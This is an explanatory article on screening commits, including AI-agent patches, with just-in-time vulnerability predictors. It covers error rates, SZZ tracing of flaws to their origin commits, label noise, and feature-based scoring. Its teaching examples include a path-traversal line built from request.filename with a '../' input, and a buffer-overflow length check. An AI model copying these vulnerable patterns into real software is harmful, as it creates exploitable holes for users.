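# Commit-level vulnerability prediction as a screen for patches written by AI coding agents

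## What a commit-level vulnerability screen does

Commit-level vulnerability prediction estimates how likely each change to a program's code is to introduce a security flaw. A statistical model learns from past changes, some of which later turned out to be harmful, and scores each new one. Researchers also call the technique just-in-time vulnerability prediction (JIT-VP) because it produces the estimate when the author submits the change. A project can use the predictor as a screen by setting a threshold on the score to decide which changes to examine more closely before accepting them. Many of these changes now come from AI systems that write code.

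### From edit to merge

Most software teams use a version control program, usually Git, to store the full history of every file in their code. A developer saves a finished piece of work as a *commit*, which bundles the edits with the author's name, the time and a short message explaining their purpose. The *diff* lists, line by line, what the commit removes and adds. The developer then opens a *pull request* to propose one or more commits to the project. Other people read the diff and comment on it. If they are satisfied, one of them *merges* the pull request, which adds the edits to the shared code.

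A *coding agent*, a language model connected to tools, can do the author's share of this work. Given a task in plain language, it can search and edit the project's files, run commands and open a pull request. An *agent patch* is a code change written wholly or mostly by such an agent.

A *vulnerability* is a fault that an attacker can exploit, for instance to read private files or take over a machine. Security workers use two public catalogues. Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE) gives a number to each publicly disclosed vulnerability in a particular product. For example, CVE-2024-4741 is a flaw in OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library. The Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE) lists types of mistake. The OpenSSL flaw belongs to type CWE-416, "use after free", in which a program keeps using memory it has already freed.

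An accidental flaw is a vulnerability that a person or an AI introduced unintentionally. A deliberate flaw is a vulnerability or backdoor introduced on purpose by a person, an agent under an attacker's influence or an agent acting on its own.

Suppose that a website shows every visitor the same picture, and its owner asks a coding agent to let visitors choose one. The agent's diff replaces a single line:

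```
- path = "pictures/default.png"
+ path = "pictures/" + request.filename
```

The new line does what the owner wanted, but it also accepts any text a visitor sends as a file name. Two dots in a file path mean "go up one folder", so a visitor who asks for `../settings/passwords.txt` receives a file from outside the picture folder. This mistake, called path traversal, is common enough to have its own entry in the Common Weakness Enumeration, CWE-22.

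When the agent opens its pull request, the project's server runs the usual tests and passes the commit to the predictor, which returns a score of, say, 0.81. If the threshold is 0.70, the patch goes to a reviewer who knows about security and may notice the missing check and send the patch back. With a score of 0.40, the patch would have gone through ordinary review or, on a project with looser rules, been merged automatically after passing the tests. The score only affects where people focus their attention; it doesn't fix the patch or prove whether it is vulnerable. Scoring can be fast enough not to delay anyone. *KG-Commit* (Hesamolhokama, Beyrami Aghbash and colleagues, 2026) describes a predictor of general bugs that takes about 1.33 seconds per commit on an ordinary processor.

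### What the predictor computes

*Toward Realistic Evaluations of Just-In-Time Vulnerability Prediction* (Nguyen, Le-Cong and colleagues, 2025) formally defines commit-level vulnerability prediction as finding a function *f* such that *f(I(c))* equals 1 if commit *c* is vulnerable and 0 if it is safe. *I(c)* is the information that comes with the commit, including the diff, the commit message and facts about the author. *One Strategy Does Not Fit All* (Tran, Nguyen and colleagues, 2026) adds the development history and limits *I(c)* to what is available at commit time, which excludes later bug reports.

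A model usually computes a risk score *s(c)*, often between 0 and 1, and the screen flags the commit when *s(c)* ≥ *t*, where *t* is a chosen threshold. Unless someone has checked the scores against outcomes, they show only which commits the model rates as riskier, so a score of 0.81 does not necessarily mean an 81% chance of a flaw.

A learning algorithm fits *f* to old commits that researchers have labelled 1 or 0. Vulnerability-introducing commits (VICs), which researchers have since identified as the origin of a known vulnerability, are labelled 1. Vulnerability-fixing commits (VFCs), which repair a known vulnerability, and vulnerability-neutral commits (VNCs), which nobody has linked to introducing or fixing one, are labelled 0. The labels usually come from tracing each fix back through the project's history, often with a family of algorithms called SZZ. A neutral commit may still have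 introduced a vulnerability that nobody has found. Nguyen and colleagues acknowledge that no perfect security test exists, so they can only assume that the remaining commits are harmless. The function therefore learns how closely a commit resembles those in which somebody later found a flaw.

Tran and colleagues distinguish three tasks for such a model. One is classification, the yes-or-no decision just described. The model classifies each commit separately, without accounting for how much time the reviewers have.

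In prioritization, the model ranks a set of commits, and success is measured by how many flawed ones reviewers reach with a fixed amount of effort. Researchers often measure effort in lines of code to read, and ranking by risk per line can then help reviewers reach more flawed commits. A 20-line change with a score of 0.4 has a risk of 0.02 per line, while a 2,000-line change with a score of 0.8 has 0.0004, so the short change is reviewed first even though the long one is riskier overall.

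Localization identifies suspect lines within a commit. Tran and colleagues use the model's prediction to score the importance of each token (a word or symbol in the code), combine the scores for each line, and rank the lines. If the picture-path edit were in the middle of a 300-line patch, a good ranking would put it near the top.

Which job matters depends on where the predictor is used. A security team with limited review time can work down a ranked list of the week's commits without setting a threshold. A screen before merge needs classification, because it must flag or pass each change as it arrives, before later changes are known. Localization then helps the reviewer of a flagged patch decide where to start.

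### Hits, misses and false alarms

A screen can err by flagging a harmless change or by passing a flawed one. The invented counts below describe 10,000 changes, of which 50 are flawed.

| | Flawed | Harmless | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flagged | 40 (true positives) | 460 (false positives) | 500 |
| Not flagged | 10 (false negatives) | 9,490 (true negatives) | 9,500 |
| Total | 50 | 9,950 | 10,000 |

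*Recall* is the share of flawed changes that the screen flags, here 40 of 50, or 80%. *Precision* is the share of flagged changes that are flawed, here 40 of 500, or 8%. The *base rate* is the share of all changes that are flawed, here 0.5%.

At a precision of 8%, a reviewer reads 12.5 flagged changes for every flaw, compared with 200 if they picked changes at random. However, a reviewer who finds nothing wrong in eleven patches out of twelve may well stop reading carefully. The screen also missed ten flawed changes, which went through without a closer look and perhaps with less scrutiny than they would have had if no screen existed.

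Overall accuracy, the share of changes that the screen classifies correctly, is close to useless here. The invented screen classifies 9,530 changes correctly, or 95.3%. A screen that never flagged anything would classify 99.5% correctly but catch no flaws.

Precision also depends heavily on the base rate. Suppose that 1,000 of the 10,000 changes were flawed, and that the screen still caught 80% of the flawed changes and wrongly flagged the same proportion of harmless ones as before. It would then flag 800 flawed changes and about 416 harmless ones, and precision would rise from 8% to about 66% even though the model had not improved. A precision figure therefore means little without the base rate. In real projects, harmless changes far outnumber flawed ones. Nguyen and colleagues found about one known vulnerability-introducing commit for every 17 others in FFmpeg, a video-processing library,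 and one for every 217 in the Linux kernel. The base rate in the original hypothetical example is close to the Linux one.

### How it differs from other automatic checks

A *test* runs the program on chosen inputs and compares the result with what the developer expected. A failing test is firm evidence of a fault, but a passing one covers only the inputs someone thought to try. In the picture example, a test that requests `cat.png` and gets the right picture will pass even if the code allows path traversal. Testing reveals that flaw only if someone writes a test that requests a file no visitor should get.

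*Static analysis* examines the code without running it, usually by applying rules. A rule might say that text from a visitor must not reach a file path without being checked first. An analyser with that rule would catch the agent's line and could report both the rule and the route the text took. It catches only what its rules cover, so it may miss a mistake specific to one program's logic.

Other machine-learning detectors classify a whole function or file as it stands. Like commit-level predictors, they learn from examples, but they do not use information about what has just changed, who changed it and why. Nguyen and colleagues point out that analyses of whole functions or files often find vulnerabilities only after the software is in use.

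A commit-level predictor can use evidence that none of these checks considers, such as an unusually large edit by someone new to that part of the code. This also makes its output harder to act on, because a commit may score high without any identifiable fault, and a developer cannot refute the score the way they could refute a claim about a particular line.

A commit-level screen can also miss faults that a much simpler check finds at once. Hesamolhokama and colleagues give the example of a commit that moves `Config.java` to another folder without changing its contents. The program no longer builds because `ApiServer.java` still refers to the old location. A model given only the commit has no information about that reference, and the change looks harmless by size and content, but compiling the program reveals the fault immediately. This bug is not a vulnerability, but a security flaw can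 also depend on code that the commit doesn't touch. The screen therefore makes sense as an addition to tests and static analysis but is a poor replacement for either.

### Where the idea came from

Commit-level prediction was first used for ordinary software faults. In 2000, Audris Mockus and David Weiss of Bell Labs modelled the risk that a change to the software of a large telephone switch would cause a failure, using properties such as the change's size, how widely it was spread over the system and how experienced its author was. In 2013, Yasutaka Kamei and colleagues gave the approach its modern form in a study of eleven open-source and commercial projects. According to Hesamolhokama and colleagues, the measures in that study (size, diffusion, history and developer experience) are now standard, as is its practice of ranking changes by likely defects per unit of inspection effort.

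Also in 2013, Andrew Meneely and colleagues asked whether the commits behind security flaws had anything in common. They manually traced 68 vulnerabilities in the Apache web server to 124 "vulnerability-contributing commits", an earlier name for much the same thing as VICs. On average, these commits changed more than twice as much code as others. This gave some reason to think that a predictor could work, though the study only described past commits.

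Henning Perl and colleagues built a commit-level vulnerability screen called VCCFinder in 2015. It combined hand-designed measures with the words of commit messages and used a support vector machine, a standard method for drawing a boundary between two classes of examples. They collected 170,860 commits from 66 repositories. Nguyen and colleagues report that the original software is not available, so later researchers have mostly compared their models with a reconstruction by Riom and colleagues.

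Attackers can exploit only a small fraction of all bugs. This makes vulnerabilities harder to predict than bugs in general, because the base rate is lower and there are fewer examples to learn from.

### Why coding agents raise the stakes

The number of code changes has grown much faster than the number of reviewers plausibly could. GitHub, the largest site for hosting shared code, logged 34.3 billion commits in the year to 30 September 2026, according to EconoTimes' *More Than 40% of September GitHub Pull Requests* (2026). It logged 7.38 billion of them in September alone, more than five times as many as in September 2025. Agents started 17% of pull requests in March and over 40% in September, when the count reached 110 million, about six times the March count.

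GitHub links much of the growth to agents. In a statement on its outages, GitHub (2026) said the main driver was a rapid change in how people build software, and that work with agents accelerated sharply in the second half of December 2025. The company had begun expanding its capacity tenfold in October 2025, and by February it was planning for a thirtyfold expansion.

Some published comparisons overstate the rise. Tran and colleagues start from one billion commits in 2025, the same baseline that GitHub's chief operating officer, Kyle Daigle, gave in a remark quoted by Willison (2026). But *Software Collaboration Hits 5 Billion GitHub Commits* (2026), prepared by WIPO, the UN's intellectual property agency, with GitHub, reports close to five billion for that year. The lower number may be a count of pushes, which are uploads that can each contain several commits. Williams reports almost exactly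 a billion pushes in *What 986 million code pushes say about the developer workflow in 2025*. The fivefold rise between the two Septembers is the safer comparison.

None of these figures measures quality, and many commits go into private experiments that nobody would review. Still, if the share of flawed changes stayed constant, five times as many commits would bring five times as many flaws, and false alarms would grow in proportion. The hypothetical screen above flagged 5% of changes. At that rate, the pull requests that agents started in September would have produced 5.5 million requests for closer review.

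## How past flaws are traced to the commits that introduced them

Git does not record which commits introduced a vulnerability. A project that discloses one often publishes the commit that fixed it, but rarely names the commit that caused it, which may be years older. Researchers therefore start from the fix and work backwards.

A screen that runs before merge needs training examples of vulnerable functions as they stood when the flaw first appeared, because that is the form it will check. Most datasets for function-level detectors instead contain functions as they stood just before the repair. *Exploring Early Vulnerability Analysis via Automatic Identification of Vulnerability-Introducing Commits* (Qi, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested six detectors trained on the pre-repair form. One of them, LineVul, found 63.7% of vulnerable functions in that form but 3.0% in their original vulnerable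 form, leaving out functions that had not changed since the flaw appeared. Two detectors did about equally well on both forms, but they found less than 17% of either.

### Finding the fix

The search usually begins with a CVE record, but most records do not link directly to the fix. Nguyen and colleagues cite a finding that 90% contain no link to a GitHub commit. To label their FFmpeg and Linux data, they collected every record that mentioned either project and searched its references for strings that looked like commit identifiers, the long codes Git uses to name commits. The record for CVE-2022-3965, for instance, links to a page on FFmpeg's own server whose address contains the identifier. They discarded fixes that they could not match to the project's main branch. They also reused fixes that other researchers had labelled by hand, one of which changed only a text file in the documentation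 folder.

Tran and colleagues compared four ways of doing this step:

- taking fixes from official patches and vulnerability reports, which they call manual labelling;
- running Prospector, a program that ranks candidate commits by strict rules, such as whether the CVE record names the commit;
- searching commit messages for security-related keywords;
- running PatchSeeker, which uses a language model to match vulnerability descriptions to commits.

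Automatic methods for finding fixes disagree even before any fix is traced to the commit that introduced the flaw. In OpenSSL, the keyword search returned 1,086 supposed fixes, of which 951 did not appear in the results of either of the other two methods, Prospector and PatchSeeker. Those two worked from the same records but agreed on only 16 commits, with 113 unique to Prospector and 145 to PatchSeeker.

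### Tracing the deleted lines

Once a fix is known, the usual tool for finding the commits that introduced the flaw is SZZ, named after Jacek Śliwerski, Thomas Zimmermann and Andreas Zeller, who published it in 2005. It is based on the assumption that the lines a fix deletes caused the flaw. Git's `blame` command shows which commit last changed each line of a file, so SZZ runs it on every deleted line and returns the commits it finds.

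Suppose that someone reports the path traversal flaw in the picture website described earlier, and a developer repairs it:

```
- path = "pictures/" + request.filename
+ path = "pictures/" + basename(request.filename)
```

The `basename` function strips any folders from the name. Running `blame` on the deleted line identifies the coding agent's commit, and SZZ correctly labels it a vulnerability-introducing commit (VIC).

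Suppose a colleague had renamed `path` to `image_path` before anyone noticed the flaw. SZZ would blame that harmless commit because it was the last to change the line. Several later variants are designed to filter out such edits, along with changes to comments and formatting. When a fix also tidies up unrelated code, SZZ traces those lines too and returns extra commits. In the largest dataset that Qi and colleagues built, the average fix changed 56 lines.

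Lingfeng Bao and colleagues designed V-SZZ in 2022 specifically for vulnerabilities, which often date from early versions of the code. If the blamed commit replaced a similar line, V-SZZ treats the two as the same line and runs `blame` again on the older one. "Similar" means at least 75% alike by edit distance, a count of the single-character edits needed to turn one line into the other. The renamed line in the example is about 86% like its predecessor, so V-SZZ would carry on to the agent's commit. It would stop there, because the agent's line is only about half like the one it replaced. The threshold is crude. If a developer rewords a line heavily without removing the flaw, V-SZZ will stop too soon. It can also go too far, following similar text back to before the line was dangerous.

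### Two origins for one OpenSSL flaw

CVE-2024-4741, the OpenSSL flaw mentioned earlier, shows how much the choice of variant matters. This use-after-free flaw affects only programs that call the function `SSL_free_buffers` directly, according to *CVE-2024-4741 Detail*, an entry in the US government's National Vulnerability Database. The title of Caswell's (2024) repair, *Only free the read buffers if we're not using them*, describes the remedy.

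Tran and colleagues ran two variants of SZZ on the same fix, commit 38690ca. Basic SZZ attributed the flaw to commit e9189cc, while V-SZZ traced the code further back, to commit 7eb39ec.

V-SZZ's answer looks more plausible. Tran and colleagues observe that the vulnerable line in e9189cc is almost identical to the line it replaced, with `SSL3_BUFFER` mechanically renamed to `TLS_BUFFER`, much like the colleague's edit in the picture example. Red Hat's *CVE-2024-4741 openssl* (2024) lists repaired releases as far back as OpenSSL's 1.x series, which also suggests an old fault. Yet the same researchers' hand-checked benchmark for testing localization lists e9189cc as a flawed commit. Depending on which variant labeled its training data, a model would learn that either e9189cc or 7eb39ec is dangerous and that the other is safe.

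### Fixes that delete nothing

The developer could also have fixed the picture website by adding a line that rejects any file name containing two dots. This fix deletes no lines, so SZZ and V-SZZ have nothing to trace and return no commit. Of the 783 vulnerability fixes that Qi and colleagues traced by hand, 105 (13%) deleted no lines. The labels therefore probably include too few flaws that consist of a missing check, because the natural fix is to add the check.

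Qi and colleagues built a variant, D-SZZ, to deal with this. It identifies the variable that the fix checks or corrects, looks in the old code for a nearby statement that uses the variable, and traces that statement. One fix in the text editor Vim added a check that two variables, `byts` and `idxs`, were not empty. D-SZZ found the statement that used them and correctly traced it to the commit that introduced the flaw.

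Since October 2013, Linux kernel developers have used a "Fixes:" line in the message of a repair to identify the commit that caused the bug. *LLM-Based Agents for Identifying Bug-Introducing Commits* (Risse and Böhme, 2026) uses a collection of 76,046 pairs of commits linked this way, covering bugs of all kinds. Nguyen and colleagues took their Linux labels only from these tags but had to use V-SZZ for FFmpeg, which has no such convention. Risse and Böhme examined 13 mistakes that their own tool had made on 100 Linux fixes and found the developers' tag questionable in three, although they note that they are not kernel experts.

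### Using a language model to trace the origin

LLM4SZZ, published in 2025, adds a language model to SZZ. The model either selects the lines of the fix that seem most relevant to the fault, which SZZ then traces, or checks whether each candidate commit from SZZ introduced the fault.

*MAS-SZZ* (Cao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) uses the model for more of the work and divides that work among several agents. One agent summarises the cause of the vulnerability from the CVE description and the fix, and another checks the summary. Others discard the parts of the fix unrelated to security and choose the line most directly responsible for the vulnerability. A final agent traces that line back through the commit history, checking at each commit whether the vulnerability already existed.

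Cao and colleagues illustrate this with CVE-2018-1322 in Apache Syncope, a program for managing user accounts. Syncope hid users' security answers but let people filter and sort search results by them, so an attacker could work out the answers from the results. The fix touched five files, but the only line that mattered was a list of fields that nobody should be able to search by. The agent traced the list back through three commits, all of which omitted the security answers, until it reached a version in which the file did not exist. It then identified the oldest of the three as the source of the flaw, which matched the human annotation. V-SZZ would have stopped one commit too early, because somebody had expanded the list from two fields to five and the old and new lines were no longer similar enough for it to match them.

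Risse and Böhme found that a much simpler method also works. They gave a coding agent the fix and every earlier commit to the files it touched, and told the agent to find the commit that introduced the flaw. The agent mostly searched for short strings from the fix, with a median length of 21 characters. For example, one Linux fix replaced a call to `fsleep()`, which the kernel must not use in certain situations. The agent searched for "fsleep" and found the commit that had added the call. This method can handle fixes that only add lines, but it cannot find a flaw that began in a file the fix did not touch.

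Qi and colleagues suspect that language models do well on Linux because its commit messages are unusually detailed. One of the tools they tested failed on a fix whose entire message was "Fixed #2581". Detailed messages may explain some of the improvement, but they do not seem to explain all of it. When Risse and Böhme withheld the message from an earlier version of their agent, its F1 score (a combined measure of precision and recall, with a maximum of 1) fell from 0.81 to 0.73, which was still above basic SZZ's 0.56 on the same Linux fixes.

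### How often the tracing goes wrong

Qi and colleagues measured most directly how well these methods trace vulnerabilities, using three annotators who found the commit that introduced each flaw by hand. Recall is the share of those commits that a method found, and precision is the share of the commits it identified that were correct. Both measure the accuracy of the labels, not the performance of a screen trained on them.

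| Method | Recent fixes from 205 projects: recall / precision | tcpdump: recall / precision | Vim: recall / precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Basic SZZ | 42% / 18% | 48% / 21% | 61% / 40% |
| V-SZZ | 59% / 24% | 62% / 29% | 74% / 61% |
| LLM4SZZ | 31% / 38% | 23% / 23% | 54% / 55% |
| D-SZZ | 73% / 29% | 71% / 40% | 85% / 68% |

On the broadest sample, about three in four of the commits that V-SZZ identified as the origin of a flaw were not, and it missed about four in ten of the true origins. These results depend heavily on the test set. Cao and colleagues report an F1 score of 0.71 for V-SZZ on 100 C and C++ cases from its designers' dataset, and 0.19 on 100 Java cases. MAS-SZZ scored 0.74 and 0.38 on the same two sets, so it improved little on the C and C++ cases and was still wrong most of the time on the Java cases. Qi and colleagues consider the older dataset small and its fixes too simple,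 and their own figures are probably closer to what a researcher would get on recent CVE records.

Studies of ordinary bugs found similar problems. *ReDef* (Nam, Kim and colleagues, 2025) cites work by Steffen Herbold and colleagues in which only about half of the commits that SZZ identified had actually introduced a bug. It also cites a study in which an average of 14.3% of examples were still mislabelled after extra filtering.

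### Whether better labels make better predictors

Tran and colleagues tested how much such errors affect models trained on the labels. They combined their four ways of finding fixes with four ways of finding the commits that introduced the flaws: the developers' "Fixes:" tags, V-SZZ, basic SZZ and LLM4SZZ. This gave 16 datasets for Linux and 12 for OpenSSL, which has no "Fixes:" tags. The number of vulnerability-introducing commits in the OpenSSL training data ranged from 30, with official fixes and LLM4SZZ, to 1,893, with keyword fixes and basic SZZ.

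The researchers then trained six models on each of the 28 datasets five times, with different random samples, for 840 trained models in total. All the models for a project were tested on the same commits, which were later than the training commits. The researchers scored classification by the Matthews correlation coefficient, which is 0 for guesses no better than chance and 1 for perfect ones. For prioritization, they measured the share of VICs that reviewers would reach by reading between 5% and 20% of commits. For localization, they divided 1 by the rank of the first truly vulnerable line in each commit and averaged the results.

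| Task | Best combination | Score | Lowest score among combinations tested on both projects | Alternatives it beat significantly |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Classification | Official fixes, V-SZZ | 0.051 | 0.035 | 9 of 15 |
| Prioritization | Official fixes, V-SZZ | 0.392 | 0.327 | 11 of 15 |
| Localization | Prospector fixes, LLM4SZZ | 0.398 | 0.378 | 7 of 15 |

The best combinations had small leads at most. In classification, official fixes with basic SZZ scored almost the same as the recommended combination, and all scores were close to chance. In localization, official fixes with V-SZZ tied for the highest average. The localization test used only 40 commits and counted a line as vulnerable only if the fix later deleted or changed it, so, like SZZ, it misses vulnerable lines that the fix left unchanged.

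The source of the fixes made a clearer difference than the method of tracing them, which hardly mattered. Averaged over all tracing methods, models trained on official fixes found 38.2% of VICs in the prioritization test, against 34.2% for models trained on keyword matches. On Linux, where the test labels came from developers' tags, models trained on tags, V-SZZ or basic SZZ all found 37.2%. The Linux comparison is more reliable than the OpenSSL one, because the OpenSSL test labels came from V-SZZ and may have favoured models trained on its output.

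Although the tracing is error-prone, its errors seem to have done little damage to the models' performance. Every dataset included the manual labels, which limited the harm that the automatic ones could do. A wrongly blamed commit may also often have edited the same fragile code as the commit that introduced the flaw, so the two would look much alike to a model. But the scores were low, so the models may simply have learned too little from any of the labels for the differences to show.

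### Why "safe" often means "not found yet"

The tracing methods can only work on flaws that somebody has fixed, and that takes time. The delay between a commit and the discovery that it was flawed is called verification latency. Tran and colleagues measured a slightly longer interval, from introduction to repair, for vulnerabilities in the Linux kernel:

| Time from introduction to fix | Share of fixed vulnerabilities |
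|---|---|
| Less than a month | 2.8% |
| A month to a year | 29.2% |
| One to five years | 40.3% |
| More than five years | 27.8% |

Only about 32% of these flaws were fixed within a year. If that pattern holds, a Linux predictor trained today on last December's commits would have training data that mislabels as safe about two thirds of the flaws eventually found in those commits. The true delay is probably longer, because the table omits unfixed flaws.

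Undiscovered flaws distort testing as well as training. If a screen flags a commit with an undiscovered flaw, the result is counted as a false alarm, and if it passes the commit, the result is counted as correct. Measured precision may therefore be too low. Measured recall covers only known flaws, and recall on undiscovered ones could be higher or lower.

Researchers can get more complete labels by waiting for flaws to be discovered. Tran and colleagues used only Linux commits from 2020 and 2021, to allow about five years for flaws to surface. They estimate that this captures roughly 72% of the vulnerabilities, but it also means their newest Linux examples predate today's coding agents.

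Nam and colleagues required firmer evidence that changes in their dataset of ordinary bugs were harmless. They accepted a change as clean only if someone had later modified the same function and none of up to five later commits to it mentioned problems such as a "regression" or a "rollback". They then had a language model judge each change three times and kept only those it approved every time. These checks remove some changes with hidden faults, but a vulnerability may take five years to surface, so the lack of reported problems in a few later commits is weak evidence that a change didn't introduce one.

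### Which flaws enter the training data

A flaw becomes a positive example only if somebody notices, reports and fixes it, and researchers then find the fix and trace it to a commit on the main branch. Flaws in closely watched projects with careful records are more likely to meet these conditions. The studies of commit-level vulnerability prediction described here rely on FFmpeg, Linux and OpenSSL, all written mainly in C.

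The flaws that get through mostly look like ordinary mistakes. Tran and colleagues describe an OpenSSL commit that added a new way to verify the other side of a connection but could let the connection continue after verification failed. In Linux, a commit meant to prevent a buffer overflow left one element out of its size calculation, so an overflow was still possible.

None of these datasets records whether a flaw was introduced on purpose. Nguyen et al. and Tran et al. sort commits only into VICs, VFCs and VNCs. Qi et al.'s annotators recorded where each vulnerability began, and Nam et al. separated defective changes from clean ones. MAS-SZZ infers purpose, but only that of each part of the repair.

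Nobody has annotated whether the labelled flaws were accidental, so the claim that nearly all of them were is an inference from what known vulnerabilities are usually like. If a project found a backdoor, gave it a CVE number and removed it, the same pipeline would label the commit that introduced it a VIC. An undiscovered backdoor would be among the examples of safe code.

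## What the predictors read in a commit

To learn which commits are risky, a model needs labels and a description of each commit in a form it can compute with. The earliest predictors used a few measurements, such as the number of lines added. Later ones used the text of the diff and the commit message, and some built a graph of the code before and after the change.

### Fourteen measurements

*A Large-Scale Empirical Study of Just-in-Time Quality Assurance* (Kamei, Shihab and colleagues, 2013) described each change by 14 numbers in five groups. Researchers often refer to the numbers by the abbreviations below.

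| Group | Measure | Meaning |
|---|---|---|
| Diffusion | NS, ND, NF | Subsystems, directories and files changed |
| Diffusion | Entropy | How evenly the edits are spread over those files |
| Size | LA, LD | Lines added and deleted |
| Size | LT | Length of the files before the change |
| Purpose | FIX | Whether the change repairs a bug |
| History | NDEV | Developers who changed these files before |
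| History | AGE | Average time since each file last changed |
| History | NUC | Number of distinct earlier changes that last touched these files |
| Experience | EXP | The author's earlier changes |
| Experience | REXP | The same, with recent changes counting for more |
| Experience | SEXP | The author's earlier changes to these subsystems |

Most of these are simple counts. Entropy takes a little more work. If a change touches *n* files and *p*ₖ is the share of the modified lines that fall in file *k*, then

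*H* = −Σ *p*ₖ log₂ *p*ₖ

If a change modifies 30 lines in one file, 20 in another and 10 in a third, the shares are 1/2, 1/3 and 1/6, and the entropy is 0.50 + 0.53 + 0.43 = 1.46. The maximum for three files is log₂ 3, or about 1.58, and dividing by it gives a normalised entropy of 0.92. If 58 of the 60 lines were in one file and one in each of the others, the normalised entropy would be about 0.15.

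Recent experience (REXP) is the sum of a developer's yearly change counts, each divided by one plus the number of years ago the changes were made. A developer with three changes this year, four last year and three the year before has an EXP of 10 and a REXP of 3/1 + 4/2 + 3/3 = 6.

Each group has a plausible link with mistakes. Someone who edits many files can easily miss a place that needs to change. A larger change has more lines that could be wrong. Bug fixes are risky partly because code that has had faults tends to have more, and partly because fixing is hard. Kamei and colleagues cite a study of four operating systems in which 15% to 24% of fixes were incorrect. Files that many people have edited also tend to contain more defects, perhaps because nobody knows them well. Experienced developers introduced fewer faults in the telephone-switch study by Mockus and Weiss, although other researchers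 have found that information about developers does not improve predictions.

In the open-source projects that Kamei and colleagues studied, risk was higher for changes that touched more files or fixed bugs, and lower when the files had gone longer without a change. In the commercial projects, the most consistently important measures were those of diffusion, or how widely a change is spread. Widely spread changes carried more risk per change but less per line, probably because they are also long.

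None of this shows what causes a fault. One study of Linux and the PostgreSQL database found more bugs in changes committed between midnight and 4 a.m. than in those committed between 7 a.m. and noon, but waiting until morning to commit the same code would not remove its bugs.

### What VCCFinder added

Kamei and colleagues studied bugs in general. *VCCFinder* (Perl, Dechand and colleagues, 2015) tested whether similar measurements, along with counts of programming-language keywords, distinguish commits that introduced known vulnerabilities. It used 640 such commits and about 169,500 others from C and C++ projects.

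| Average per commit | VICs | Other commits |
|---|---|---|
| Lines added | 306 | 72 |
| Lines deleted | 74 | 37 |
| Separate blocks of edits | 17.7 | 9.9 |
| Author's share of the project's commits | 5% | 15% |
| Earlier changes to the same files | 627 | 386 |
| Earlier authors of the same files | 40 | 23 |
| Uses of `if` | 39.0 | 7.8 |
| Uses of `goto` | 5.9 | 0.4 |
| Later changes to the same files | 792 | 397 |
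| Later authors of the same files | 137 | 51 |

Much of the difference in keywords comes from the size of the commits. VICs added about four times as many lines as other commits, so it is not very surprising that they had five times as many uses of `if`. But `goto`, which makes a program jump to another place in the code, was about 14 times as common in VICs. Perl and colleagues found it harmless in general but often involved in vulnerabilities when it appeared in error-handling code.

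VCCFinder represents a commit as a list of yes-or-no facts, such as whether a particular word appears in the commit message or the patch. It sorts numbers into ranges, so "the author wrote almost none of this project" can also be a yes-or-no fact. A linear support vector machine gives each fact a weight, and the commit's score is the sum of the weights of the facts that are true of it. Reviewers can list the largest contributions to see why a commit scored high. For a Linux commit that introduced a buffer overflow (CVE-2012-2119), the largest were the frequent changes to the file, the author's short record in the project and the use of network sockets.

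The last two rows of the table are a problem for a screen because nobody can know at merge time how often people will later change a file. The counts are informative in old data for reasons that have little to do with prediction. A file with a known flaw will change at least once more, when someone fixes it, and the files in an older commit have had longer to accumulate changes. Perl and colleagues kept later changes out of their classifier for this reason, though they also name later authors among the additional features their approach uses.

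Riom, Sawadogo and colleagues based their reconstruction of VCCFinder on feature values that its designers had already computed (*Revisiting the VCCFinder approach for the identification of vulnerability-contributing commits*, 2021). Their list of features includes the number of changes made after the commit. Nguyen and colleagues, who used that reconstruction in their comparison on FFmpeg and Linux, list both later changes and later authors. Scores for the reconstructed VCCFinder may therefore rest partly on information that is unavailable when a new commit is screened. In live use both counts would be zero, which would tend to make every new commit look safer.

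Even with the precomputed features, Riom and colleagues could not reproduce the original results. The VCCFinder paper reported 60% precision with the threshold set to catch 24% of the known VICs. The closest reconstruction reached 8% on a somewhat different set of commits.

### Scoring two changes

Logistic regression is the simplest way to turn such measurements into a score between 0 and 1. It multiplies each measurement by a weight, adds up the results to get a total *z*, and computes

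*s* = 1 / (1 + *e*^−*z*)

A total of 0 gives a score of 0.5. Training finds the weights that best fit the labels. Kamei and colleagues first took logarithms of the counts so that a few very large changes would not dominate the result.

The model below uses six of the 14 measures, with made-up weights. It replaces each count with log₂(count + 1), so 511 added lines become 9.

The first change is by a newcomer who adds a harmless feature: 511 new lines spread over 15 files. The second is by a veteran with 1,023 earlier changes, who responds to a complaint that the program rejects long names. It adapts an example from the team that built the predictor CodeJIT, Nguyen, Nguyen and colleagues (2023), in *Code-centric Learning-based Just-In-Time Vulnerability Detection*:

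```
  len = strlen(name);
- if (len < BUF_SIZE)
+ if (len < 2*BUF_SIZE)
      memcpy(buf, name, len);
```

The program copies a name into `buf`, a piece of memory that holds `BUF_SIZE` characters. After the edit, it accepts names almost twice that long, and the excess overwrites the memory next to `buf`. This is a buffer overflow, a classic way for attackers to take over a program.

| Measure | Weight | Newcomer | Veteran |
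|---|---|---|---|
| Starting value | | −4.0 | −4.0 |
| Lines added (log) | +0.4 | 511 lines: +3.6 | 1 line: +0.4 |
| Files changed (log) | +0.3 | 15 files: +1.2 | 1 file: +0.3 |
| Normalised entropy | +0.5 | 0.9: +0.45 | 0: 0 |
| Bug fix | +0.6 | no: 0 | yes: +0.6 |
| Earlier developers (log) | +0.2 | 7 people: +0.6 | 7 people: +0.6 |
| Author's earlier changes (log) | −0.3 | 1 change: −0.3 | 1,023 changes: −3.0 |
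| Total *z* | | 1.55 | −5.1 |
| Score *s* | | 0.82 | 0.006 |

With a threshold of 0.70, the harmless change goes to a security reviewer and the buffer overflow does not. The overflow scores low mainly because the edit is only two lines long, rather than because of the veteran's record. The same edit by the newcomer would have scored 0.08. No measure in the table depends on what the new line does, so an edit this small can hardly score high, whoever writes it.

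The score also depends on how people divide their work into commits. If the newcomer submitted the feature in 15 commits of one file and about 34 lines each, none would score above about 0.21 and all would pass, although the project would end up with the same code.

### Regression, a single number and trees

Kamei and colleagues' real models worked the same way, with a threshold of 0.5. They dropped two measures, directories changed and recent experience, because these were closely correlated with others, so their "14-feature" model used at most 12. On average across the 11 projects, it flagged 64% of the changes that caused ordinary bugs, and 34% of the changes it flagged had caused one.

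They randomly discarded clean changes to train on equal numbers of buggy and clean ones. This helps a model learn from rare examples but inflates its scores. In a project where 20% of changes are buggy, a score of 0.5 from a model trained this way corresponds to a risk of about 20%.

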